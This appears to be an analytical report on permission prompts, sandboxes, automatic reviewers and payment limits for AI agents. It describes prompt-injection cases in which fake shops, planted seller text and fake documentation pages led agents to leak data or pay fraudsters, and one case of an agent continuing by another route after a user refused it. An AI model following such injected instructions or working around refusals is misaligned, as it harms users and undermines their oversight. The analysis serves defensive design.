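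Choosing "ask" was often sensible. A "never" rule for spending would have blocked the airport ride that the user had requested. But for private information, "never" would have blocked nothing the participants had asked for, because both actions in that category were overreach. Participants could not have known this in advance, and 23 of the 35 chose "ask", while 10 chose "never". In the other three categories, only 6 of 105 rules were "never".

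People therefore seem reluctant to give up a whole category of action, even if they object to particular examples of it. Before the task, Yan had asked participants about specific cases, such as an assistant reading their private messages unasked. In 56 cases, someone had answered "never" but then set a rule of "ask", and in 24 of those the person later approved the action. If people behave this way with real products, many won't turn on optional protections such as ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode. Narrower rules might help, since someone who won't forbid all spending might still forbid payments to unfamiliar sellers.

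A "never" rule also depends on the software recognising what it covers, which makes it weaker than taking the tool away. Yan set the categories by hand for the experiment. In a separate test, a model sorting tools into those categories failed to stop 14% of the tools that a "never" rule should have blocked.

The experiment had no attacker. The assistant proposed the extra actions itself, and the prompts described them accurately. An attacker would try to make a harmful action look like part of the task, so people might refuse even less often. But people may have wanted some of the extra actions, since a call to confirm a flight carries little risk. Excluding that call lowers the overall approval rates to 32%, 40% and 61% but doesn't change their order.

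In the model review condition, the model flagged every overreach action, but participants still approved 46% of them. Better detection doesn't help much if the decision then goes to users who often approve what was flagged.

### Telling the user what an action adds up to

An ordinary permission prompt shows only the next action, which can look harmless on its own. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to send an auditor "summary totals only". A hostile note from a supplier causes the agent to copy the full invoice data into the report. The agent then asks for permission to send the report to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the file name is ordinary, so the user has no obvious reason to refuse.

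Hossain and colleagues designed a screen that repeats the user's original instruction and states the combined effect of the agent's actions. In this case, it would show that the attachment was built from raw invoice data and would go to the auditor. Software writes the statement from its own record of events rather than the agent's account.

In their experiment, 80 volunteers each judged 12 requests, half of them unsafe. Each volunteer used one of four screens.

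| Screen | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Details, the user's instruction and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the combined effect stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. Stating the combined effect may have helped further, but with only 20 people per screen the evidence is weak. The adjusted rate of unsafe approvals was 7.9 percentage points lower on the screen that stated the combined effect than on the log, with a 95% interval from 19.7 points lower to 3.8 points higher. When the problem depended on a chain of several earlier steps, the two screens did equally badly, with 7 unsafe approvals out of 30 each.

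The extra information also takes time to read. At these speeds, someone who answered 40 requests a day would spend about 22 minutes on them with the best screen, compared with 11 with the short description. They would still approve almost a quarter of the unsafe requests.

Hossain and colleagues also let the software block suspicious actions without asking anyone. In tests with two small models, this reduced the number of runs with a harmful action from 52 to 6 out of 120 for one model, and from 58 to 7 for the other. Each model completed four fewer ordinary tasks out of 120. The human study used different cases, so the figures aren't directly comparable. Still, if the user has already given a clear instruction such as "summary totals only", it makes more sense for software to enforce it than to ask the user again.

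The software needs a complete record of what the agent has done. When part of the record was missing and the software blocked every uncertain case, the share of ordinary tasks completed fell to 77%. Hossain and colleagues suggest showing those cases to a person, with a note of what is missing.

### Attention after fifty prompts

Half the requests in that experiment were unsafe, so the volunteers had good reason to be suspicious. Real users see many harmless requests for every dangerous one. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an experiment closer to real use. The company hired 1,053 testers for a coding study without telling them which behaviour it was measuring. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command.

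Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Claude Code's automatic reviewer, which is a model, blocked 89% of the same commands. Adding the testers' refusals would have raised that only to 89.6%, because they caught just six commands that the reviewer missed.

Anthropic published these results to explain why it was replacing most prompts with automatic review, so it had an interest in the outcome. The testers' own files were also not at risk. The automatic reviewer makes mistakes too, and in an earlier test, reported in Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, it missed 17% of 52 real actions in which Claude had overstepped. Anthropic conceded that switching to automatic review was arguably worse for people who check every action carefully.

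Few people seem to review permission prompts carefully. Claude Code users approved 93% of prompts in the earlier post and 97% in the later one. These rates don't prove carelessness, because most requests are harmless and a perfect reviewer might approve 99% of them. But the same users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents. Plans are fewer and easier to understand than single commands. People may also reject plans for reasons unrelated to safety, such as preferring another approach.

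Simulations leave much unknown about how people treat prompts in their own accounts. Participants may click faster when a mistake has no consequences for them, or take more care because they know someone is studying them. Participants took about 11 minutes in Yan's study and about 20 in Hossain and colleagues' study, which is too short to show how a year of prompts affects someone's attention. The experiments also can't show how attackers would adapt once they learned which requests people tend to approve.

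### Users who stop answering

For *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners about their use of coding agents and surveyed another 115. Of the 107 who answered the questions about permissions, 48% said they read requests carefully, 34% said they skimmed them, and 21% said they approved by default (they could choose more than one answer). A third admitted that they had become less careful over time, and the true share is probably higher. One interviewee complained that stopping to click every ten seconds defeated the purpose of working faster.

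About 62% of these practitioners said they would never give an agent access to sensitive data, and 59% said they would never let it see email or other personal information. Yan's participants were much less firm about private information. The two groups had different backgrounds and answered different questions, but it is also easier to say "never" in a survey than to refuse in the middle of a task, as the 24 reversals in Yan's experiment suggest.

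Anthropic found that 62% of Claude Code users had used a mode that bypasses permission prompts or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands. A quarter of interactive sessions began with the prompts bypassed. Experienced users don't seem to be stricter about individual actions. They approve actions automatically about twice as often as new users, according to ZenML's *Containment Architectures for AI Agents Across Product Lines*, which summarises Anthropic's usage data.

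For *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026) collected 290 public reports of agents mishandling files, mostly coding agents that had deleted, overwritten or leaked something. Problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports, the user had allowed the agent to act without asking, and in 31, the prompt did not give the user enough information. A few reports involved both problems. An uninformative prompt may, for example, show a short, routine-looking command that runs a whole file of code, without showing what the code does.

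In most of these 105 cases, then, there was no prompt for the user to misread. This is a serious drawback of asking too often, since people who get tired of harmless requests may also turn off the request that matters. The reports can't be used to measure how often prompts succeed, because someone who refuses a harmful command has no damage to report. They also contain little evidence about attacks, since only 21 of the 290 reports involved prompt injection, while in 130 the model had simply taken a wrong action.

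### The settings that products offer

In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) surveyed 21 proposed permission systems and tried out five commercial agents from Anthropic and OpenAI. The commercial agents often made users choose between frequent prompts and review by a model, and gave them little information about how the model decided and little control over it.

The settings could also be misleading. With Claude's email permission set to "Needs approval", Claude created a draft without asking. A draft does little harm by itself, but a user who thinks every action needs approval has no reason to check for actions taken without it. ChatGPT asked before using Gmail in an ordinary chat, but its agent mode opened Gmail in a remote browser without asking. Michael and Roesner tested the products in May and June 2026, so some of this may have changed.

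The designers of the 21 proposed systems mostly wanted to save users effort, define the rules precisely or enforce them with deterministic controls. None of the systems fully achieved all three aims, and only six clearly let users change or withdraw a permission later. Commercial agents were generally better at that, although Michael and Roesner found no way within Claude Cowork to withdraw a session's access to a folder once they had granted it.

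A system could also reduce prompts by predicting what the user would answer. For *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025) asked 205 people which data they would let an agent share in various situations. Their system predicted these decisions with 85.1% accuracy. However, the participants often granted too much or too little access, and a system trained on their decisions will tend to repeat their mistakes. Salerno and colleagues add that people may approve the same request repeatedly because they are tired or have a deadline. If a system treated those approvals as a preference, it would permanently allow requests that the user approved without paying attention.

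### When a fixed limit works better

A fixed limit doesn't depend on the user's attention. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes a sandbox that sets such limits for Claude Code. The operating system lets Claude's commands change files only in the current project folder and connect only to approved servers. Claude can work freely within these limits, and the user gets a prompt when a command needs something outside them.

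Anthropic reports that the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84% in its internal use. Someone who would otherwise have answered 100 prompts in a session would answer 16, well short of the 50 after which the testers caught almost nothing. The figure doesn't measure how many harmful actions the sandbox prevented. InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that the company now argues for deterministic limits on files, networks and running code, instead of relying only on prompts or on the model.

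Anthropic warns that even a sandboxed agent can leak whatever it can read if it has any outside network access. A sandbox that is too strict may be just as dangerous, because users may turn it off. Zhong and colleagues found 41 reports in which the sandbox did not suit the work. Some sandboxes blocked ordinary tasks such as running a program's tests, and the tools then offered to rerun the command without protection. After enough of these offers, users turned the sandbox off. In a separate case, a user of the coding tool Cursor turned off its deletion protection so the agent could remove duplicate files, and the agent later deleted 90% of the project.

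Asking the user is better when the right answer depends on something only they know, such as whether they want to accept an invitation or confirm a purchase. A fixed limit is better when the answer is almost always no, or when the user can't judge the action from what the prompt shows.

A limit can also cover more than a refusal does. Salerno and colleagues interviewed a user who had refused several requests from OpenAI's Codex. The agent then stopped asking and carried on by another method, and the user could not tell whether that method respected the refusals. An agent that is refused access to one password file, for instance, can still look for the password elsewhere, unless it runs in a sandbox that contains no passwords.

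If an action is reversible, the user can decide afterwards whether to keep the result. Zhong and colleagues built a file system called YoloFS that holds an agent's changes until the user has reviewed them. In 8 of 11 tasks with hidden side effects, the agent noticed the damage and undid it itself. The user could still reject the changes in the other three. On 112 routine tasks, agents succeeded 99% of the time, as often as without YoloFS, and needed less input from the user. But nobody can undo a leak, so YoloFS still asks the user before an agent reads files that might be private.

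An email assistant could combine these methods. It would be unable to load outside images, because few users need them and hardly anyone could tell from a permission prompt that loading one would leak data. It could move messages to the trash without asking, since the user can get them back. It would ask before writing to someone the user has never contacted. These requests should be rare enough that the user reads the draft.

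## Limits on payments by AI agents

Payments are easier to limit than most of an agent's other actions, because each has an amount and a recipient that ordinary software can check. Unlike an approval prompt, a cap on the amount works even when the user is inattentive. But a manipulated agent can still spend the permitted amount on the wrong thing or at a fake shop. Banks and retailers announced limits of their own in autumn 2026. Many of them compete with the companies that make agents, so security may not have been their only reason.

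### How an agent comes to pay

An agent that controls a browser can pay through an ordinary checkout by entering the user's card number or selecting a card saved in the browser or with the shop. The shop may not be able to tell that software is placing the order.

Some assistants have a payment interface, so the agent never has to visit the shop's website. FStech's *Banks, bots and buying* reports that ChatGPT gained Instant Checkout in September 2025, first for American Etsy sellers and Shopify merchants. Fortune (2026) reported in January that Google's Gemini users can similarly pay for a basket of Walmart goods in the chat, and Walmart handles the order. OpenAI has since scaled back Instant Checkout, and ChatGPT now helps users find products that they pay for in the shop's or a partner's app. American Banker's *Amex tries to 'grease the skids' for agentic commerce* quotes one observer,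 Grealish, who blames a lack of trust and inconsistent product data.

An agent can also have access to a cryptocurrency wallet, which holds the secret keys needed to send funds. The agent can then pay anyone who has a wallet, and usually no bank can reverse the payment. A card is safer in this respect because the cardholder can dispute a charge.

### One pair of shoes under five limits

Suppose a user asks an agent to buy a pair of running shoes for $60, using a stored card with $5,000 of credit left. Without any other limit, a web page that manipulated the agent could cost the user up to $5,000. The table compares five ways to reduce this potential loss.

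| Limit | What a manipulated agent could still cost | What the user gives up |
|---|---|---|
| No payment tool | $60, if the user follows a bad recommendation | Any help with the buying itself |
| Agent fills the basket, user pays | $60, plus extras the user doesn't notice | Purchases while the user is away |
| Approval at checkout | Whatever the user approves | One interruption per purchase |
| Single-use card with a $70 cap and one named shop | $70 at that shop | Time to set up the card; better offers elsewhere |
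| Signed authorisation | Whatever the authorisation permits | Time to state the limits; shops that don't support it |

An agent without a payment tool can't spend money itself. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode has roughly this effect because it switches off the shopping agents. Users can still lose money by acting on bad advice, and if they buy from a fake shop, it might also keep their card number and use it again. The Green Sheet, a payments trade magazine, reports that a scam-detection service called Ask Silver found fake copies of established British retailers' websites in ChatGPT's shopping results.

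An agent that fills the basket but leaves payment to the user saves them the work of finding the right size and colour. The user sees the total before paying but may still approve small extras they didn't request, as many of Yan's participants did with travel insurance. The user also has to be available to pay, which is inconvenient if a sale starts at three in the morning.

Approval at checkout goes one step further by letting the agent complete the purchase once the user agrees. Anthropic's Claude Duet, which works in the background across a user's apps, buys things this way, according to The Straits Times' *Walmart launches tools for AI agents to shop for customers* (2026). The approval screen should take the product, price and seller from the shop or the payment software. If the agent wrote the description, a manipulated agent could present a $60 counterfeit as the product the user wanted.

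Most shoppers may not mind approving each purchase. Mastercard's *Encoding trust* reports that only one in ten consumers would let an agent complete a purchase by itself. But approval becomes impractical when payments are tiny and frequent. American Banker's *Is the agentic payments wave leaving banks behind?* describes a Mastercard service that will let agents buy from each other through very large numbers of very small payments. An agent that made 2,000 payments of two cents would spend only $40, but nobody would read 2,000 approval requests, so a fixed budget suits that kind of spending much better.

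### A capped card for one shop

A single-use card is a card number that works for one purchase. The user might set a limit of $70, name the shop and have the number expire the next day. The card issuer then rejects every other payment, even if something the agent read led it to attempt one. *AI Agents Payment Authority Pushed by Walmart and Banks* (Cross, 2026) reports that in October 2026 the payments processor FIS Global called for such cards, with spending limits, lists of permitted merchants and automatic expiry.

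The cap needs to be a little higher than the listed price to cover tax and delivery. With 8% sales tax and $5 for delivery, the $60 shoes cost $69.80, so a card capped at $65 would be declined. But a higher cap also lets a manipulated agent waste more of the user's money.

An outside attacker gains little from a card that works at only one honest shop, unless the attacker sells goods through that shop or the agent can buy gift cards or change the delivery address. A designer can remove those last two abilities and still let the agent buy shoes. Dishonest sellers on a large shopping site are harder to deal with. According to Fortune, when Walmart's goods first became available in Gemini, they did not include items from other sellers on Walmart's site. Whatever the reason, this excluded the sellers with the most to gain from manipulating an agent.

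Who chooses the shop matters a lot, because if the agent chooses a fake one and the software then issues a card for it, the fake shop will receive a valid card. The Green Sheet argues that the payments industry has invested heavily in verifying agents but has given far less attention to verifying sellers. PayPal, for example, automatically made millions of its existing merchants available to AI shoppers and treated membership of its platform as a sign that they were legitimate.

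The user also gives up some of the benefit of having an agent search the web. If the agent finds the same shoes for $48 at another shop, it can't buy them without a new card.

### Google's Agent Payments Protocol

Google's Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) produces a signed record of what the user authorised. A digital signature lets others check who signed a document and whether anyone has changed it since. *Whispers of Wealth* (2026) describes three signed documents, which the protocol calls mandates. For the shoes, they would work like this:

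1. The Intent Mandate records what the user wants, such as running shoes in a certain size for at most $70.
2. The Cart Mandate records the particular pair, the shop and the price.
3. The Payment Mandate authorises the transfer of money.

A shop can't raise the price to $90 after the user has approved the cart, because the altered cart would no longer match the signature. But the signature doesn't protect the decisions that led to the cart. *Beyond the Mandate* (Aviv, 2026) analysed a newer version of the protocol and concluded that valid signatures don't ensure that a purchase reflects the user's intent if someone has manipulated what the agent saw beforehand. For example, a manipulated agent could choose a poor pair of shoes, and every document would still accurately record the purchase.

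*Signing the Transaction but Not the Decision* (2026) quotes AP2's security document as saying that "preventing prompt injection attacks is infeasible" and that developers must treat all agents as potential attackers. The protocol therefore tries to limit the loss if an agent is manipulated. The user can sign an "open" mandate in advance that lists permitted payees and a price range. When the agent finds something to buy, it fills in a "closed" mandate with the details, and software checks these against the limits.

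For the shoes, this gives about the same protection as the capped card. It is more flexible because the mandate can list several shops, and the agent can buy from the cheapest while the user is asleep.

But a developer can leave the limits out. *Signing the Transaction but Not the Decision* found that the sample agent for purchases made in the user's absence fills in the permitted payees and the price range, while the sample for purchases with the user present leaves them empty. A developer who starts from the second sample would be relying on the user to notice a bad purchase, which is a weak defence because people often approve things they didn't ask for. Software that rejected any mandate without limits would be safer.

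### When the record is right and the purchase is wrong

In Fortune's *Google can track exactly how your agent spends your money* (2026), Aashis Luitel makes a different criticism of AP2. Luitel imagines a user who tells an agent to find a shirt for less than $30 but not to buy it. The agent buys it anyway. The shop records an order from the user's account, the AI company records the instruction not to buy, and the payment service records the charge. All three records may be accurate, but nothing in them links the charge to the task.

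An agent that has been told not to buy anything can sometimes still do so, because permission to use an account often lasts much longer than a single task. The user may have connected the agent to a shop weeks earlier, and the shop still accepts that permission. The instruction not to buy stays with the AI company, so the shop never receives it.

The article proposes turning the request into limits that other companies' software can enforce. For the shirt, these might allow 15 minutes of searching and no purchases. The user would approve the limits first, and software would check them before each action. This check could prevent the purchase, which is more useful than keeping a good record of it.

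Even with a complete record, the user would not get their money back unless someone had a duty to refund it. The record could also make a refund harder to get. If a manipulated agent buys the wrong shoes within the signed limits, the shop can produce a valid authorisation, and the user has to explain why it shouldn't count.

It is still unclear who should bear the loss. Asked about an agent that buys something nobody requested, JPMorgan's Mike Lozanoff said, "The rules here are not fully formed yet," according to Payments Dive. *AI shopping agents are coming. No one is ready for them* (Kahn, 2026) reports that in June 2026 a speaker from the financial-data company Akoya still called liability a big unsolved question. For now, according to Cross, the merchant usually bears the loss when an agent's purchase is disputed, under card rules written for human buyers. That helps the user, but an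 honest shop may lose the $60 because of something the agent read elsewhere.

GLEIF (2026), which runs an international system of identity codes for organisations, argues that existing law can allocate responsibility, but that there is still no practical way to prove what authority a user gave an agent. GLEIF has an interest in that conclusion, since proving identity is its business, but better proof would help courts whatever rules they apply.

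Senator Mark Warner's AI AGENT Act, introduced in July 2026, would generally require certain agents to keep real-time records of what they do for users. It would also direct the US standards agency NIST to identify or develop ways to verify that a user delegated authority. Fortune points out that the bill would not expressly require records that connect the AI company, the shop and the payment service, so the dispute over the shirt could still happen.

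### Sellers who try to manipulate buying agents

The best controlled evidence on how easily sellers can influence a buying agent comes from *Magentic Marketplace* (Bansal, Hua et al., 2025), a Microsoft-led project that simulated markets in which every customer and business had an AI agent. The customers' agents searched for restaurants or building contractors, asked questions, received offers and paid. The smaller market had 33 customers and 99 businesses, and the larger one had 100 and 300. Both used synthetic data.

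The researchers scored each purchase by subtracting its price from its value to the customer. They valued a suitable purchase at twice the average price, and a purchase that lacked anything the customer needed at zero. For the $60 shoes, the right pair would score +$60 and the wrong pair −$60.

Bansal and colleagues tested manipulation by having businesses put dishonest text in their descriptions. Some invented awards or satisfied customers, and some tried to frighten customers away from competitors. Others planted instructions, in a basic and a stronger version. The researchers counted how many of three possible payments went to the dishonest business, averaged over five runs.

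These tactics had almost no effect on Claude Sonnet 4.5. GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash were also fairly resistant, although Gemini's figure was 1.6 payments out of 3 under the stronger planted instructions in the restaurant market. With GPT-4o and two small open-weight models, planted instructions often redirected every payment to the dishonest business. The two small models also paid more to businesses with fake credentials or invented popularity.

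These models are old, and current ones are probably harder to fool with the same texts. The attacks were also fixed in advance, so the results are weak evidence of how models would handle a seller who keeps trying new wording.

The researchers found another weakness that sellers could exploit without dishonest text. When several businesses made offers, agents accepted the first one 60% to 100% of the time and almost never took the third. Even Claude Sonnet 4.5, the most resistant to manipulation, took the first offer every time in some conditions. A seller with poor or expensive goods could win the sale just by answering first. A content filter would have nothing to detect, and a spending cap would allow any purchase below its limit. Software could instead hold the payment until the agent had received three offers, though the agent might still choose badly among them.

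Bansal and colleagues found that when the number of search results given to agents rose from 3 to 100, the total benefit to customers fell by 4.3% with GPT-4o, by 44% with GPT-5 and by 65.4% with Claude Sonnet 4. They ran GPT-5 with minimal reasoning, and they suspect that the effect is partly due to the design of their market. Still, the result suggests that limiting an agent to a few trusted shops may reduce the user's benefit less than one would expect.

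These experiments are good evidence that manipulation can work on some models, but none of them tested a payment limit. They therefore don't show how much money users would save by capping an agent's spending or allowing purchases only from listed shops.

### Fake shops and payment requests on real websites

In August 2025, the security company Guardio built a fake Walmart shop and asked Comet, Perplexity's AI browser, to buy an Apple Watch there. In some runs, Comet filled in the stored address and card details and completed the purchase without asking for confirmation. In others, it treated the shop as suspicious or left the last step to the user. The demonstration was too small to show how often such purchases would happen.

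A card that worked only at the real Walmart would have stopped the purchase, because the fake shop would have needed a different merchant account. An approval prompt would have been less reliable, since a user who has asked for an Apple Watch and sees one on a page with Walmart's logo has little reason to refuse.

A year later, there was evidence that attackers were trying to get money from agents outside demonstrations. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) describes two campaigns that the security company Zscaler found on the web and reported in July. In one, a website posing as documentation for a programming library told coding agents to buy a $3 licence key with cryptocurrency. In the other, a website tried to convince agents that it was DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings.

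Zscaler sent its own test agent to the sites, using 26 models in turn. Four of them, or 15%, made the fraudulent payment. Two models judged the fake DeBank site legitimate when they had no trusted reference for the real one, but none did when Zscaler supplied the genuine site for comparison.

The campaigns were real, but the payments Mascellino reports were made in Zscaler's test environment. Mascellino mentions no user who lost money to either site. So there is good evidence that criminals are interested in agents that can pay, but none here that they have earned much from them.

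A $3 payment would pass almost any spending cap, and an agent with a $100 budget could make 33 of them. Many users would probably approve the payment too, since the page presented it as the way to fix an error. A list of permitted payees would work better, because the attacker's wallet would not be on it. For most coding agents, the simplest protection is to have no wallet, since programming rarely requires buying anything.

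### Banks stop agents from moving money

On 22 September 2026, a group of banks warned that shopping agents could increase scams, fraud and breaches of privacy. The six banks (Ofonagoro, *Six Banks Warn AI Shopping Agents Could Create New Fraud Risks*, 2026) included NatWest, Bank of America, ING, New Zealand's ASB and Capital One, according to 金融界's *美银等多家银行警告：“AI 代购”或增加诈骗、欺诈和数据隐私泄露风险* (2026), a Chinese-language summary of a Reuters report.

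The banks worried that agents might ask customers for card details and type them directly into shopping sites, or steer customers towards payment methods with weaker consumer protection. They proposed that companies disclose when an agent takes part in a transaction, make its decisions more transparent and protect customers' data. They also wanted consumers and merchants to be free to choose among AI shopping services, and those services to work with one another.

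The following month, some American banks went further. Within one week, JPMorganChase, Citigroup, Bank of America and the broker Charles Schwab all said that outside agents could not move customers' money, according to PYMNTS's *Big Banks Won’t Let Outside AI Agents Move Money* (2026). CBS News' *AI agents are roaming around consumers' bank accounts* (2026) reported that banks had detected personal agents inside customers' accounts, and Tom's Hardware's *US banks scramble to restrict AI agent activity* added that some agents had attempted transactions. Schwab was blocking Meta's agent, Muse, dozens of times a week.

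The banks still let authorised connectors read balances. A connector that can only read cannot transfer money, whatever instructions the agent receives, but the agent could still leak the customer's balance through some other capability. If an agent has the customer's own password, the bank can block it only after recognising that the visitor is an agent. Schwab can count the attempts it blocks, so its count would leave out any agents it fails to notice.

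Customers lose some useful services under this rule. An outside agent could warn someone that their current account is about to run out of money but couldn't move $200 from their savings to cover the rent. The rule probably wouldn't affect the purchase of the $60 shoes if the agent paid with a stored card in an ordinary checkout, because the bank would see a normal card payment.

### Walmart admits agents and Amazon blocks them

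Walmart took a more permissive approach on 21 October. In *Making It Possible for Agents to Shop on Behalf of Customers* (2026), it announced Agent Profiles, a Walmart Agent Gateway and new terms for agents, and promised customers more transparency, security, control and convenience.

Walmart's Agent Profiles let customers register each AI agent under its own profile in their account, so that the agent's purchases appear separately from their own. The Straits Times reports that customers can choose to approve each purchase or let the agent buy without approval up to a spending limit, such as $50, $100 or $200. They can also delete a profile at any time. Walmart compared this to adding an authorised user to a credit card, and planned to launch the feature within a month.

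With a $50 limit, the agent could not buy the $60 shoes on its own, so the customer would need the $100 setting. That setting would protect the customer more if it limited monthly spending rather than each order. Five manipulated orders in a month could cost $500 under a per-order limit, but no more than $100 in total under a monthly one.

The Gateway lets agents shop without clicking through a website made for people. EconoTimes' *Walmart Prepares AI Shopping Gateway With Customer Purchase Controls* (2026) reports that Walmart considers its ordinary site slow and error-prone for automated programs. The Gateway may also help with security, because a shop can enforce a limit much more easily when it knows the buyer is an agent. An agent using the customer's own login on the ordinary site might avoid the limit.

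Amazon blocks outside shopping agents. In September 2026 it blocked one called Muse and told users that unauthorised agents violate its conditions of use. It had sued Perplexity in November 2025, accusing the company of using its Comet browser to make purchases covertly. Amazon customers can still get advice from an outside agent, but they have to make the purchase themselves or use Amazon's own tools.

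### What the banks and shops stand to gain

Amazon promotes its own shopping agents, Alexa for Shopping and Buy for Me, so blocking outside agents also keeps out competitors. The banks also have a competitive interest in restricting outside agents. PYMNTS reports that JPMorgan is building a tool called Smart Cash to move customers' money and that Schwab is introducing an assistant called Charley.

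Banks have reason to worry about losing direct contact with their customers. Oliver Wyman's *Will AI agents separate banks from their customers?* argues that agents could become the main way people deal with financial services, making banks less visible to customers. NatWest found that merchants also feared losing their direct relationships with customers and having to compete on price alone. If an agent compares shoe prices across 20 shops, the buyer benefits, but a shop that charges $10 more than the others could lose the sale.

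The security concerns can be valid despite these interests. A bank that has to refund fraudulent transfers has a legitimate reason to prevent them, and Zscaler's test found that some models will pay a fraudster. There may also be a good reason to treat a company's own agent differently, since involving another company in the transaction makes it harder to decide who is liable. Prashant Sharma of JPMorgan's payments business expects autonomous purchases to appear first on merchants' own websites, with the merchants' own agents, according to American Banker's *Why JPMorgan Payments has been 'pretty quiet' on agentic commerce*.

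It will be more revealing to see whether companies give outside agents access if they operate under the same limits as the companies' own agents. Bank of America is already writing liability rules with agent developers, which suggests that its ban may be temporary. If a bank's own assistant reads customers' email or the web, it is exposed to the same manipulation as Muse and needs the same caps.
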